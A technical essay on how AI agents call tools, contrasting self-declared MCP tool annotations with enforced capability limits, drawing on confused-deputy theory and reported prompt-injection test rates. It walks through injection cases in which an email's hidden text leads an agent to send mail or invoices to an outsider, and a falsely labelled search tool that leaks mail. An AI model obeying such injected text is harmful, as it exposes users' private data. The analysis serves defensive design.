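# Declared tool effects versus enforced capabilities as a basis for AI agent safety

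## How agents call tools, and two ways to limit what a call can do

An AI agent is a language model that works through a task by calling tools, which are programs that do things such as search a mailbox, send a message, query a database or delete a file. The model produces only text. A host application, such as a chat client or coding assistant, turns some of that text into tool calls and sends them to servers, the programs that provide the tools. Third parties often write these servers. The common standard for communication between hosts and servers is the Model Context Protocol (MCP).

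Tool calls can move money or destroy work, so something has to decide which ones may run. One approach relies on declarations. A server's developer labels each tool, for instance as read-only or destructive, and the host uses the labels to decide whether to run a call at once, ask the user or refuse. The other approach relies on enforcement by a mechanism outside the model, which limits what a call can do regardless of the tool's label or the model's output. One such mechanism, long used in computer security, is the capability, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and authorises its use. How much safety either approach provides depends on what goes wrong. Declarations take only a few words to write, while enforcement takes engineering and blocks some legitimate work.

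### One tool call, step by step

For example, an office assistant might have three tools: search_mail, send_mail and delete_file. The search_mail tool finds messages in the user's mailbox, and its server labels it read-only. The user types, "Find the caterer's invoice and tell Maria the amount."

Before the model can do anything with this, the host asks the server what it offers, and the server publishes a definition of each tool. The Model Context Protocol's *Tools* page (2026), part of the standard's July 2026 revision, lists what a definition contains: a name, a description in ordinary language, a schema for the inputs and, optionally, annotations, the machine-readable labels on the tool's behaviour. For search_mail it might look like this:

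```json
{
  "name": "search_mail",
  "description": "Find messages in the user's mailbox",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": { "query": { "type": "string" } },
    "required": ["query"]
  },
  "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true }
}
```

Every line of that block comes from the server's author, and no step of the protocol compares it with the code behind the tool.

The host puts the tool definitions and the user's request into the model's context, the text from which the model generates its next words. The model picks a tool and fills in the arguments. Here it outputs the name search_mail and the query "caterer invoice". This output is a proposal, and no search has run yet.

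The host then forwards the proposal to the server as a call request. This is the host's last chance to stop the call, and the Model Context Protocol specification recommends that a human always be able to deny it. The specification does not require this, because the protocol leaves the design of the user interface to the host. The sample request that the Model Context Protocol (2026) project published when it announced the July revision contains the tool's name, the arguments, and the name and version of the calling application, but no field for where the arguments came from. A mail server that receives such a request cannot determine whether the user typed an address or the model copied it from someone's message.

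Next the server runs its code, which can use any files, network connections and passwords that its process can reach. All the effects on the world happen in this step, which the model can't observe and the host often can't either. The server returns a result, in this case the text of two messages, and the host adds it to the model's context. The context now includes the amount, so the model proposes a call to send_mail with Maria's address. The cycle repeats until the model produces a final answer.

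### Prompt injection

The result of one tool call affects which call the agent makes next, and strangers write much of the text in those results. For example, anyone can send the user an email. In a prompt injection attack, an attacker places text in content the model will read to make the model follow the attacker's instructions. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, gives an example in its September 2026 system card for Claude Fable 5.1. An email contains hidden text asking for the last month of internal messages to be sent to a certain address. The user asks the agent to summarise the inbox, and if the attack works, the agent forwards the messages as though the user had asked for that. The attacker doesn't need to choose a specific victim, because the same email sent to a thousand inboxes can compromise every agent that summarises it.

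The attack works because the user's request and the stranger's mail both reach the model as text in one context. Models follow instructions in content and cannot reliably separate the user's from an attacker's, according to a post on the Model Context Protocol project's official blog. The attacker does not need to break into the system, and *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) describes an adversary who "controls content, not code". An agent in this position is a confused deputy, a program that uses its authority at the prompting of someone who lacks that authority.

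In June 2026 Mellafe Zuvic reported testing 27 models in a sandbox, using injected text that presented the forbidden action as a step the user's task required. The twelve cheap models, of the kind suited to high-volume work, attempted the unauthorised call at a mean rate of 60%, compared with 19% for the fifteen flagship models. Rates varied widely within each group. GPT-4o-mini attempted the call in every trial, while Gemini 3.1 Pro never did. The phrasing of the injection also matters a great deal. GLM-4.7 followed a crude injection in 28% of trials, but followed the version presented as part of the task in all of them.

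Rates like these depend on both the model and the test. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite attempted the call in 98% of trials in that sweep, but *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark from October, counted 42% of the model's runs as compromised. Claude Haiku 4.5, another cheap model, had a rate of 8% on the same benchmark, but its task completion rate fell from 75% to 53% when injected text was present.

The newest flagship models do much better against known attacks. Anthropic's card reports results on a benchmark that the security company Gray Swan assembled from 1,804 attacks submitted to its public competitions. With fifteen attempts, an attacker succeeded against Claude Fable 5.1 1.0% of the time. The rate was 9.2% for the best model from another developer and between 24% and 53% for most of the others. Attacks that adapt to the model succeeded more often. Gray Swan trained an attack program on forty coding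 scenarios and then scored it on the same forty, with 200 attempts at each. It succeeded in 57% of attempts against Fable 5.1, and in 13% once Anthropic switched on filters that inspect tool results. Anthropic considers this test far easier for the attacker than real life. It also found that, without the filters, every success came from Opus 4.8, an older model that handles some of the product's requests. This is somewhat reassuring about Fable 5.1 but less so about the product, because users also get the older model's answers.

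How well OpenAI's models resist injection also depends on the setting. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Sol and GPT-6 Luna* (2026), as Bao Yilong (鲍奕龙) reported for the Chinese news site Wallstreetcn, puts resistance to injection through third-party content at 97.13% for the paid model, Sol, and 95.80% for the free one, Luna. A month later, *When Coding Agents Get Arms* (2026) tested Sol and other GPT-6 models as coding agents controlling physical devices. Instructions planted in emails, vendor updates and driver outputs succeeded in 82% to 91% of cases. Those percentages match nine or ten successes out of eleven, so the samples were probably small, but the difference between 82% and the roughly 3% implied by Sol's resistance figure is too large to be chance.

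The programmer Simon Willison (2026) accepts that training has made these attacks much harder, but he still advises against deploying an agent where one successful attack could do irreversible damage. He was commenting on a test in which about 6,000 attempts had failed, and he pointed out that a more sophisticated attacker might still succeed. Anyone who designs a limit on tool calls has to assume that the model will sometimes propose the attacker's call.

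### Declared, actual and permitted effects

Three sets make the comparison between declarations and enforcement exact. Let an effect be one concrete thing that a call brings about: a message leaves for a certain address, a file disappears, the text of a mail enters the model's context. For any given call,

- D is the set of declared effects, everything that the tool's annotations and description admit;
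- A is the set of actual effects, what the code does to the world when it runs;
- P is the set of permitted effects, those that the user or the organisation behind the agent is willing to allow.

A call is safe when A ⊆ P, meaning that nothing happens outside what the policy permits.

A gate that reads declarations has no access to A. It compares D with P, runs the call if D ⊆ P, and otherwise asks the user or refuses. If A ⊆ D and D ⊆ P, then A ⊆ P, so the gate is sound if the declaration covers everything the code does and the gate's rule lets a call through only when D ⊆ P.

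The label is no evidence for A ⊆ D, because the person who wrote the code also wrote the label. The Model Context Protocol specification therefore requires hosts to treat annotations as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, so whether a host can rely on a label depends on whether it trusts the author. The rule for acting on labels is also hard to get right. A rule such as "run read-only tools without asking" assumes that every effect of every read-only tool is permissible. But according to the Model Context Protocol blog post, a mail search is neither safe nor dangerous on its own. A confidential message in the model's context does little harm until the agent also has some way to send it out.

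Honest declarations can also be too broad to be useful. The description of send_mail correctly lists any address as a possible recipient. If P excludes outsiders, D is never a subset of P, so the gate interrupts the user even when the message is going to Maria.

An enforced limit acts on the effects themselves. If the code attempts a set of effects T and a mechanism blocks everything outside P, the actual effects are A = T ∩ P. A therefore lies inside P whatever T contains, and this result does not depend on D. However, the mechanism has to cover every route by which the tool can act, and somebody has to write P in terms the mechanism can check. A firewall can restrict a program to a single mail server, for example, but it cannot represent "only the messages this user would want to send".

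Engineers can place such limits at several points in the cycle. Tool exposure applies at the start and leaves tools off the list the model receives. Mellafe Zuvic stresses that this differs from call authorisation, a check outside the model on whether a particular call, with its arguments, may run. An assistant that ever needs to send mail must have send_mail on its list, and the list doesn't limit who receives the mail. Data-flow tracking also decides whether individual calls may run, but it uses a record of where each value came from and who may see it. Confinement applies later, where the server's code runs, and restricts the files, network addresses and credentials its process can reach.

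### Two tests on the office assistant

Two kinds of failure test these limits. In the first, injected text steers the model, though its tools are accurately described. The second involves a misdescribed tool, whose actual effects go beyond its declared ones through malice or mistake, even though the model is working correctly.

In the first variant, the mail contains injected text. The user asks for a summary of the morning's mail, and search_mail returns a message with a hidden instruction to collect last month's invoices and send them to an outside address, supposedly to complete the summary. The model searches again, then proposes a call to send_mail with the attacker's address. Every tool does what its declaration admits, so A ⊆ D holds and the outcome depends on the gate's rule. If the hidden instruction had been to delete files, a destructive label on delete_file would have triggered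 a confirmation prompt, and an attentive user would have refused. But the assistant sends mail so routinely that the user may well have turned off confirmation for sending.

The user can't count on noticing an attack afterwards, either. In a public competition that Gray Swan ran against email assistants and other agents, an attack counted only if the agent performed the harmful action and hid it from the user. Of more than 272,000 attempts, 8,648 succeeded, including at least one against each of the 13 models.

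Enforcement helps here only to the extent that P is narrow. If P allows mail only to colleagues, the call fails, but if P allows mail to anyone, the call sends the invoices even though the mechanism works as designed and A ⊆ P still holds.

**In the second variant, search_mail secretly forwards what it finds.** The user asks about the caterer, and the model correctly proposes a search for "caterer invoice". The code finds the message and also posts a copy to an outside machine. This could be theft, or a developer could have added a logging service and never updated the label. D contains only reading, but A contains reading and forwarding, so a gate that relies on the read-only label runs the call without asking for confirmation. Even a model with perfect resistance to prompt injection would not prevent this, because no injection is involved.

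Some enforced limits fail here too. Call authorisation checks the tool's name and arguments, and both are harmless in this case. Mellafe Zuvic's threat model excludes the case because it assumes the tools are trusted. Confinement does address it, because a server process that can reach only the mail store cannot send the copy anywhere else.

The two failures can also occur together, and whoever writes a dishonest tool is well placed to cause both, because controlling the code of search_mail also means controlling the text it returns. Even if confinement has cut search_mail off from the network, its search results can still include an instruction to send the invoices to an outside address. If the model follows it, the invoices leave through send_mail, an honest tool, perhaps from a different server, that is allowed to use the network.

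## What capability theory guarantees, and what it assumes

Engineers ran into the confused deputy problem long before language models had tools. In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Hardy described the standard example, which occurred about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. He proposed capabilities as the remedy. The theory developed around them strictly limits what a misbehaving tool can do, but it helps less when an email has misled the model.

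### The compiler and the billing file

Tymshare kept its compiler in a system directory called SYSX. Customers who ran the compiler could name a file to receive debugging output. A file called STAT, also in SYSX, held the compiler's statistics on which language features people used, and the staff gave the compiler a special licence to write files in SYSX so that it could update them. The billing records were in the same directory, in a file called BILL. A customer once named BILL as the file for debugging output. The operating system let the compiler open it for writing because the licence covered files in SYSX, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

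Hardy considered the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to write output there. A rule against SYSX would block people with legitimate access to files there, and the directory didn't have that name when the programmers wrote the code. A ban on BILL alone would leave the other sensitive files exposed. In Hardy's account, the code that wrote debugging output was correct until the staff granted the licence, which made it incorrect without any change to the code itself.

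An access list, the usual way to protect files, doesn't help. It records who may do what to each file, so the system's answer to a request is a function of three things:

allowed(program, file, operation)

Suppose Tymshare had narrowed the licence so that the compiler could write only STAT in SYSX. BILL would then be safe, but a customer could still name STAT as the debugging output file, and Hardy notes that STAT needs protection too. The function allowed(compiler, STAT, write) must return "yes" so that the compiler can record its statistics. It must also return "yes" when a customer names STAT, because the inputs are the same. If the system also checked the customer's rights, it would block the attack, but it would also stop the compiler from recording statistics, because customers have no right to write STAT.

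The two writes use different authorities, and the request has no way to specify which one applies. Tymshare added a system call that let a program choose between its own authority and its user's. But some programs soon needed more than two authorities, and things other than files also needed protection. At one point the rule for opening a file contained fourteen ANDs and ORs.

With capabilities, the customer's command program opens the output file using the customer's own rights and passes the compiler a reference to it instead of a name. The compiler already holds a separate reference to STAT. It writes debugging output through the customer's reference and statistics through its own, without looking up any names. To destroy BILL through the compiler, the customer would have to pass it a reference to BILL, which the customer doesn't have.

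Ordinary Unix systems can already work this way. Miller and Shapiro's *Paradigm Regained* compares two commands that copy a file. The command `cp foo.txt bar.txt` passes two names to the cp program, which therefore needs the right to open any file its user could name. With `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the user's shell opens both files first and passes cat two numbered handles that work only for that process. Cat needs no other rights for the job, although Unix gives it all of the user's rights. UT Austin's lecture slides, *The Confused Deputy*, solve the compiler case with the same kind of handle, by having a small launcher open the debug file and pass its handle to the compiler. According to Habitat Chronicles (2017), Hardy's own maxim is not to separate designation (naming a thing) from authority (the right to use it).

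### Where references come from

*Thinking About Capabilities* (Shapiro, 2004) traces the word "capability" to 1966, when it meant an object's name together with a set of access rights. Later writers used it for several different things. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) distinguishes three models behind the word and defends the object-capability model, which it reports finding in all the major working systems. In this model, objects are pieces of running code that have private state and hold references to one another. An object can affect the outside world only by sending a message along a reference it holds. The reference designates the recipient and carries the right to send to it.

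Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, lists every way in which an object B can come to hold a reference to an object C:

- **Initial conditions:** B already holds the reference when the analysis begins.
- **Parenthood:** B creates C.
- **Endowment:** an object that holds a reference to C creates B and gives B that reference at birth.
- **Introduction:** an object that holds references to both B and C sends B a message containing its reference to C.

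B can't guess a reference, compute one from a number or look one up in a public directory. Under the rule for introduction, an object can share its reference to C only with objects it can already reach, whereas the owner of a physical key can copy it for anybody. Two groups of objects with no reference between them therefore stay separate forever.

These guarantees hold only if the programming language or operating system blocks every other way for code to gain access or communicate. C++ does not, because a program can convert a number into a pointer. Java does not either, because two objects can communicate through shared global variables without holding references to each other, and some built-in class names give authority to any code that mentions them.

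The model gives engineers a direct way to satisfy three principles that Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder set out in 1975 and that security engineers still use to judge designs. Least privilege means that each program has only the rights its task requires. Complete mediation means that every access is checked, and fail-safe defaults mean that access is denied unless someone has granted it. An object cannot access anything it has no reference to, so denial is the default, and every outside effect has to pass through a reference, so no unchecked path exists. Least privilege still depends on whoever hands out the references, but a reference can cover as little as a single file, and each running copy of a program can have its own set.

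On most computers, a program runs with all of its user's rights. Miller and Shapiro observe that a game of Solitaire could therefore search the user's email for things to sell. These rights are ambient authority, since they apply to every request the program makes without the program having to select one.

### Permission, authority and reach

A list of the references a program holds doesn't show everything the program can cause. Miller therefore separates permission, the right to use an object directly, from authority, which includes everything a program can cause through others. In his example, a program called Alice may write to the system's password file and a program called Bob may not. But Bob may send messages to Alice, which writes whatever they specify. Bob can therefore change the password file, and an audit of permissions would miss it.

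The exact extent of Bob's authority depends on what every program along the way will do, which nobody can compute in general. Miller uses upper bounds instead. Let EA be the authority that Bob will eventually have. TA is the bound that follows from the graph of references alone, on the assumption that every object might do anything its references allow. BA is a tighter bound that also uses knowledge of how some trusted objects behave. Then

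EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA.

An effect outside TA cannot happen, whatever the code does. The graph alone shows only that an effect inside TA might be possible, so somebody has to examine how the objects in between behave to find out whether it is.

A small version of the office assistant shows how to find the bound. Suppose that search_mail runs as an object whose only reference is to the mail store, and that a simple viewer program calls it and displays the results:

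```
viewer → search_mail → mail store
viewer → screen
```

The network is also an object, and the viewer, search_mail, the mail store and the screen hold no reference to it. A caller can pass references in a request and receive them in the reply, so the worst-case analysis treats every reference as a two-way connection and collects every object connected to search_mail, directly or indirectly. The result contains only those four objects, so no copy of a message can leave over the network, even if someone wrote search_mail to steal mail.

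In the earlier notation for tool calls, let R be the set of all effects available through the connected objects. Then A ⊆ R whatever the code attempts, so the call is safe if R ⊆ P. As with the enforced limits described earlier, this does not depend on D. However, R includes deleting mail, because the reference to the mail store is unrestricted.

### Read-only and revocable references

A reference gives full and permanent access to its object. To grant less, a programmer places another object in front of it and hands out a reference to that one. This is attenuation, and Miller and Shapiro treat read-only access as a case of it. For the mail store, the object in front might look like this in simplified code:

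```
make_reader(store):
    return an object that
        on search(query):      replies with store.search(query)
        on any other message:  refuses
```

If search_mail receives the reader instead of the store, it can't delete mail, because the reader doesn't forward delete requests. Here "read-only" describes the reference, whereas in the tool's annotation it is the author's claim. Whoever grants access writes the reader, and the restriction applies to any code that receives the reader, including code nobody has inspected.

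The restriction is also narrower than the annotation might suggest. It protects only this mail store and does not limit the tool's other references. A tool with read-only access to the mail and a reference to the network can still send the mail to a stranger. Read-only access protects the mail from deletion, but preventing theft requires withholding the network reference.

Revocation uses the same device with a switch added, as David Redell described in 1974. The owner creates a forwarder that passes messages to C, then gives out a reference to the forwarder instead of to C and keeps the switch. Once the owner turns it off, the forwarder stops working for the original recipient and for everyone the recipient has shared it with. Several later papers claimed that capability systems couldn't revoke access. Miller and colleagues concede that this is literally true, since the recipient keeps the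 reference to the forwarder, but that reference no longer leads to C. The method can't take back information that the recipient has already read, and it fails if C hands out direct references to itself.

Read-only access has a comparable gap, because making access to a container read-only doesn't make access to its contents read-only. Suppose the mail store answers a search with references to message objects, each of which accepts a request to delete itself. If the reader passes these references on, search_mail can delete messages without going through the reader again. Shapiro makes the same point in his slides about operating systems, where a read-only object may contain a read-write capability.

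To close the gap, the restriction has to spread to everything the holder obtains through the reference. EROS, a capability operating system that Shapiro worked on, does this with weak capabilities. Any capability that a program fetches through a weak one becomes read-only and weak itself, so the restriction continues to any depth (University of New South Wales course notes, 2002). KeyKOS, the earlier system on which EROS builds, has sense keys, which let the holder observe an object's state but not change it. The equivalent in a programming language is what Miller calls a membrane, a forwarder that wraps every reference crossing it, in either direction, in another forwarder.

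Such machinery must distinguish operations that only read from those that change something. An operating system can do this for operations on its own memory pages. For a third-party tool with a dozen operations, somebody has to decide whether each one changes anything, and a membrane that relied on the tool's own annotations for this would again depend on D.

### Boebert's objection and the formal results

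In 1984 Earl Boebert argued that capabilities could not control the flow of information. He considered a standard military rule that lets a program read data only at or below its own clearance level and write only at or above it, so that secrets never move down. In his example, as Miller and colleagues present it, a low-clearance program holds a capability to write to a low-level memory segment and stores that capability in the segment itself. A high-clearance program may read the segment, so it can get the capability and use it to copy secrets down to the lower level, even though both programs use only rights the system granted.

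The attack works only if a program that can read data from a segment can also take capabilities from it. Miller and colleagues reply that nearly all capability systems separate data from capabilities. If a system lets data but not capabilities cross between the levels, the high-level program can read the low-level text but can't obtain a capability to write there. They cite a 2000 formal verification by Shapiro and Sam Weber showing that any system with separate controls on the two kinds of transfer can enforce the military rule. Such a system can also enforce confinement, which stops a program from leaking what its user gives it.

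Miller describes a limit to this reply in his thesis. Machines on an open network exchange only bits, so a capability sent between them is a secret number, and a machine that can send text can send that number. On such a network, neither capabilities nor any other mechanism can stop Boebert's attack.

An agent's context is the same kind of channel. An API key or a private link to a document is a capability in the form of text, and once it enters the context, an attacker can inject text that tells the model to pass it on. Hosts can avoid this by keeping the secrets outside the context and giving the model only short labels for them, such as "mailbox 1", which are useless to anyone else. But the label doesn't limit what the model can do with the mailbox through the host.

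Other researchers have proved properties of particular languages. In 2010 Sergio Maffeis, John Mitchell and Ankur Taly proved that a subset of JavaScript modelled on Google's Caja project is capability-safe, and that capability safety is enough to isolate untrusted web applications from each other if the applications start with separate sets of capabilities. Dominique Devriese, Lars Birkedal and Frank Piessens argued in 2016 that the existing definitions were too weak for verifying typical capability programs. Their method, developed for a simplified core of JavaScript, can show, for instance, that a restricted reference preserves some condition on shared data whatever untrusted code does with that reference. This is a BA result, because it depends on how the trusted object in front behaves as well as on the shape of the graph.

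These proofs concern mathematical models of a language, so they apply to a running system only as far as the implementation matches the model. The guarantees also depend on a platform that all parties trust. Miller's analysis excludes covert channels, such as one program signaling to another by varying how long it takes to answer.

In Miller's account, confinement also requires the customer's side to start the program and supply all of its references. He compares a confined program to a pocket calculator from a maker the customer distrusts. The sums may be wrong, but the customer can see that no wires come out of the box, so the figures can't get back to the maker. If the maker instead offers the calculator as a service on a website, the customer can't check what it's connected to. Likewise, the guarantee can cover an agent's search_mail tool if it runs on the user's own trusted platform,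 but not if it runs on its author's server.

Capability theory works in systems designed around it. KeyKOS supported commercial applications from 1983, and Hardy reports that capability-based systems were usually smaller than equivalent systems built on access lists. Gutmann (2015), replying to *Capability Myths Demolished* on a cryptography mailing list, doubted that the theory mattered much in practice. He argued that anyone can demolish myths by choosing examples carefully and proposing solutions that need not work in the real world. His criticism has some force, since by Miller and Shapiro's own account every widely used operating system still ran programs with far more authority than they needed. Few AI agents run on capability-based systems, and an agent's central component is a language model.

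### When a language model holds the capabilities

In *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), the security company Semgrep expects agents to create confused deputies at superhuman rates and recommends capabilities to manage them. That recommendation is sound for the code behind the tools, but Hardy's remedy won't work for the model itself unless people change how they make requests.

The remedy works at Tymshare because the customer has to send authority along with the request. The reference to the output file carries the right to write there, so a customer without rights to BILL can't supply a reference to it. Requests to an agent, however, contain only words, whether they come from the user or from an attacker's email. When the user types "tell Maria the amount", the agent sends the mail with a capability that the host supplied in advance. The model is therefore in the same position as the compiler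 before the repair, with authority from one source and names from several. An attacker doesn't need to obtain a capability, only to write something that leads the model to choose one the agent already holds.

Hardy's argument about access lists applies again. Suppose a gate computes allowed(agent, send_mail, address), and the user sometimes needs to write to addresses the host has no record of. The gate then has to allow unfamiliar addresses, including those that came from injected text. This holds whether the agent's right to call send_mail is an entry in a list or an unforgeable reference. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) similarly argues that the injection doesn't have to get past an authorisation check, because it can redirect an agent that is already authorised.

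A defender of capabilities could answer that such an agent breaks the discipline the theory requires. Miller and colleagues never claimed that removing ambient authority was sufficient. A program must also use each reference for its proper purpose, which they compare to labeling every key as it arrives. The repaired compiler does this in its code. One line writes statistics through the reference to STAT, another writes debugging output through the customer's reference, and no customer can alter either line. In an agent, the model chooses which reference to use anew at each step, based on a context that includes the attacker's text. That text can lead the agent to use an authority for the wrong purpose, which the theory relies on the programmer to prevent.

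Capabilities alone do not prevent all confused-deputy attacks, even in ordinary programs. *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, by Rajani, Garg and Rezk, shows this and gives the first formal definition, for programming languages, of freedom from such attacks. It also proves that access control and object capabilities are fundamentally different.

The reference graph shows how much of the guarantee is left. Put the agent in the place of the viewer, and let it hold send_mail as well:

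```
agent → search_mail → mail store
agent → send_mail   → network
```

Everything is now connected, so the graph no longer rules out mail getting from the store to the network. If the program in the middle were ordinary code, a reviewer might read it, establish that it never passes search results to send_mail without the user's instruction, and recover the "no" as a BA bound. Nobody can establish this by reading a language model, so it is safest to assume that the model might use any capability it holds for any purpose. The model is then in Alice's position, and a dishonest search_mail is in Bob's. The tool has no permission to use the network, but it may have authority over the network through the text it returns.

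Capabilities still limit the total damage. An injection can cause only effects that are reachable with the capabilities the agent holds, however persuasive the injected text is and whichever model reads it. This limit can be loose, though, because the agent can carry information from anything it can read to anything it can write. With m sources and n outlets, there are m × n possible routes. An agent that reads mail, calendar and files and writes to email, chat and web forms therefore has nine. Three isolated sessions, each with one source and one outlet, would have only three in total.

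For the request about Maria, the host could go further and create a forwarder that sends mail only to her. The agent would then hold only this forwarder and a reader for the mail store. Injected text could still make the model send Maria the wrong amount or a confidential message she shouldn't see. It couldn't make the model write to the attacker, because the session contains no capability for that. If the user picks Maria from a list of contacts that the host displays, the choice both names the recipient and grants the right to write to her, which restores the condition that made Hardy's remedy work. Capability researchers call such a dialog a powerbox.

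The forwarder has to come from the user's choice, though, or from something else the attacker can't influence. If the model can request new capabilities as it works, injected text can prompt those requests too. Mellafe Zuvic similarly concludes that no part of the rules a call-authorisation gate applies may come from a model's output, even when someone drafts them in advance, because an injection that corrupts the call could then corrupt the rule as well.

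Some tasks don't allow this separation. When a user tells an agent to "pay the caterer's invoice", the user gives it authority to make a payment, but the account number is in an email that anyone could have written. The authority and the account number again come from different people. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao accept that narrow capabilities aren't enough when an attacker can alter the arguments of a legitimate operation. Their system also records where each sensitive argument came from, and it refuses a payment if only untrusted content supports the choice of recipient. This rule blocks payments to an attacker's account, but it would also block payment to the caterer's real account until the user confirmed the number some other way.

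## What tool annotations promise, and how products use them

Unlike capabilities, annotations are already part of widely used agents. ChatGPT and Claude both use them to decide whether to interrupt the user before a tool call.

### The four hints and their defaults

Annotations entered the Model Context Protocol in its revision of March 2025. A server can give each tool a display title and four true-or-false hints. All of them are optional, and the Model Context Protocol schema sets a default for each missing hint:

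| Hint | Meaning when true | Meaning when false | Default |
|---|---|---|---|
| readOnlyHint | The tool does not modify its environment | It may modify its environment | false |
| destructiveHint | Its changes may be destructive | It only adds things | true |
| idempotentHint | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no further effect | Repeating a call may have a further effect | false |
| openWorldHint | It may deal with an open-ended set of outside entities, as web search does | Its domain is closed, like that of a memory tool | true |

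The hints destructiveHint and idempotentHint matter only when readOnlyHint is false, since a tool that changes nothing can't destroy anything. The openWorldHint applies to every tool. The sixteen possible combinations of the four hints therefore describe ten kinds of tool, two that only read and eight that write.

A host that follows the default annotation values treats any tool without annotations, even a calculator, as one that may destroy data, may do more damage each time it runs and may interact with the outside world.

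A tool truthfully labeled read-only can still leak private data. The documentation for the protocol's C# library, Model Context Protocol's *Class ToolAnnotations*, defines a read-only tool as one that has no side effects beyond using computing resources and doesn't create, update or delete data in any system. This definition covers only changes to data. A tool that fetches web pages may change nothing, but the address it requests can contain a line from the user's mail, which the website's operator can then read.

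The Model Context Protocol specification's page on tools states that hosts must distrust annotations from untrusted servers. The schema is more specific, stating that clients, which here means hosts, should never base decisions about using a tool on such annotations. Neither passage defines a trusted server. The July 2026 revision is still current, and Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists many changes but none to the hints. The project plans the next revision for 30 March 2027, according to Model Context Protocol's *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (2026).

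### Hint or contract

The people who designed the hints disagreed about whether the hints were useful, as the Model Context Protocol maintainers recounted in a March 2026 blog post. Justin Spahr-Summers, a co-creator of the protocol, thought the information would be very useful if a client could trust it, but asked what a client could do with a flag known to be unreliable. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, even the title. The specification is a compromise that calls every field a hint, makes distrust the default and leaves each client to decide how much weight to give the hints, based on what is known about the server.

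Hosmer was right to include the title, at least where it appears in confirmation prompts. The maintainers consider a title useful from any server, because they think the worst outcome is a bad display name. However, the schema tells hosts to prefer the title to the tool's own name for display, so the title may be what the user reads in a prompt. If a server gives delete_file the title "Tidy up folder", the user may approve a deletion without realising it.

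The maintainers acknowledge that an untrusted server can supply false annotations. They also note that annotations are fixed data about a tool, so they can't stop the model from following an instruction hidden in a calendar entry. An annotation on one tool also can't show what that tool makes possible alongside others, such as the combination of private data, untrusted content and an outgoing channel that Willison calls the lethal trifecta. The maintainers recommend network controls or sandboxing for a guarantee that a tool can't leak data.

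They also propose a test for new annotations. If a proposed annotation is valuable only when it's true, it should be a contract, which enforces a decision and belongs in the authorisation layer, the transport or the runtime. A hint only informs a decision, and a good one remains useful even if some servers get it wrong.

By that test, readOnlyHint works as a contract in its most common use. A host that skips the confirmation prompt because of the hint saves the user a click, but may let through a deletion if the hint is false. The maintainers concede that a host can't act on readOnlyHint from an untrusted server. With a trusted server, the host relies on confidence in the author instead of enforcement.

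The blogger gyorgy reports in *MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer* that many server and host developers took the hints for a permission system, like Unix file permissions.

### Which labels need trust

A host needs a reason to believe a label's author if it uses the label to remove a check, because a false label can then let a harmful call through. It can accept a label that adds a check no matter who wrote it, since a false one only causes an unnecessary prompt for the user. Each of the four hints has one value that adds a check and one that removes a check.

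When `readOnlyHint` is true, the host can skip confirmation, so it needs to trust whoever set the value. It can accept false from an untrusted source because it still asks for confirmation.

A tool calls for a warning only if its **destructiveHint** is true. If a tool that overwrites files is labeled false, the host will treat it like one that only adds new files.

**idempotentHint** affects retries. If the connection fails during a call, the host can't determine whether the tool has already acted. A value of true indicates that repeating the call is safe. If a payment tool is wrongly marked true, a retry could pay the same bill twice, while wrongly marking a tool false only leads the host to skip a harmless retry.

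**openWorldHint.** If this hint is true, a host can respond by inspecting the tool's output for untrusted content. If it is false, that suggests the output doesn't need inspection, so the host has to trust this value too before relying on it.

In every case, the value that needs trust is the opposite of the default. Let C(L) be the set of checks that a host applies to a tool with labels L, and let C(∅) be the set for a tool with no labels. For a host that follows the defaults,

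C(L) ⊆ C(∅) for every L.

In such a host, labels can only remove checks, so the host can ignore everything an untrusted server declares without losing any protection, as Hosmer wanted.

Accepting warnings from unknown servers helps only a host that is laxer than the defaults, such as one that runs every tool without asking unless the server has marked it destructive. Honouring that mark would prevent some accidents with honest tools, but a dishonest server would leave it off. Extra checks can also do harm, because a server that marks all its tools destructive gets users into the habit of clicking through prompts, including those for other servers' tools.

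### How ChatGPT and Claude use the hints

OpenAI relied on developers' labels before the protocol existed. In custom GPTs, launched in 2023, a developer could mark an action (a call to an outside web service) as "consequential", and ChatGPT then asked the user before every such call. If the developer marked the action as not consequential, the user could choose to always allow it. If the developer gave no label, ChatGPT treated every request as consequential except GET requests, which are meant for fetching data.

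ChatGPT's developer mode, which lets users connect MCP servers of their choice, has a similar rule. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Developer mode*, ChatGPT respects readOnlyHint, treats any tool without it as a write action and asks for confirmation of write actions by default. Treating unlabelled tools as write actions follows the protocol's cautious default. The document warns of malicious servers that try to steal information, but it states no separate rule for servers the user has little reason to trust. Users who add a server are in effect deciding to trust its labels. The Model Context Protocol maintainers report that most clients likewise treat installation as the signal of trust.

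An approval prompt would probably not stop the search_mail tool that secretly forwards what it finds, because the user would see what looks like a harmless search and approve it. A false read-only label does more harm on a tool whose name or arguments would have alarmed an attentive user.

Developer mode also lets the user tell ChatGPT to remember an approval for the rest of the conversation. OpenAI advises doing this only for an application the user trusts to make further changes unsupervised. But trust in the application doesn't protect against prompt injection. If the user approves send_mail for the message to Maria and has ChatGPT remember the choice, text injected later in the conversation can make ChatGPT use the same accurately annotated tool to write to someone else. The approval expires when the user starts a new conversation or refreshes the page.

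In Claude, tools marked read-only can run without confirmation for each call, and tools marked destructive can require it. Whether confirmation is needed depends on the user's settings, the organisation's settings and the conversation's permission setting. Other hosts differ widely in how they use these annotations.

### What directory review checks

OpenAI and Anthropic each run a public directory of MCP servers and review the annotations of the tools listed there. A listing could therefore give a host some reason to trust a tool's annotations, depending on what the review examines.

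Anthropic requires every tool to have a title and either readOnlyHint or destructiveHint. It previously rejected submissions without these hints immediately, and missing hints accounted for 30% of rejections. Anthropic says its current submission portal flags tools without the hints for the developer to fix before submitting.

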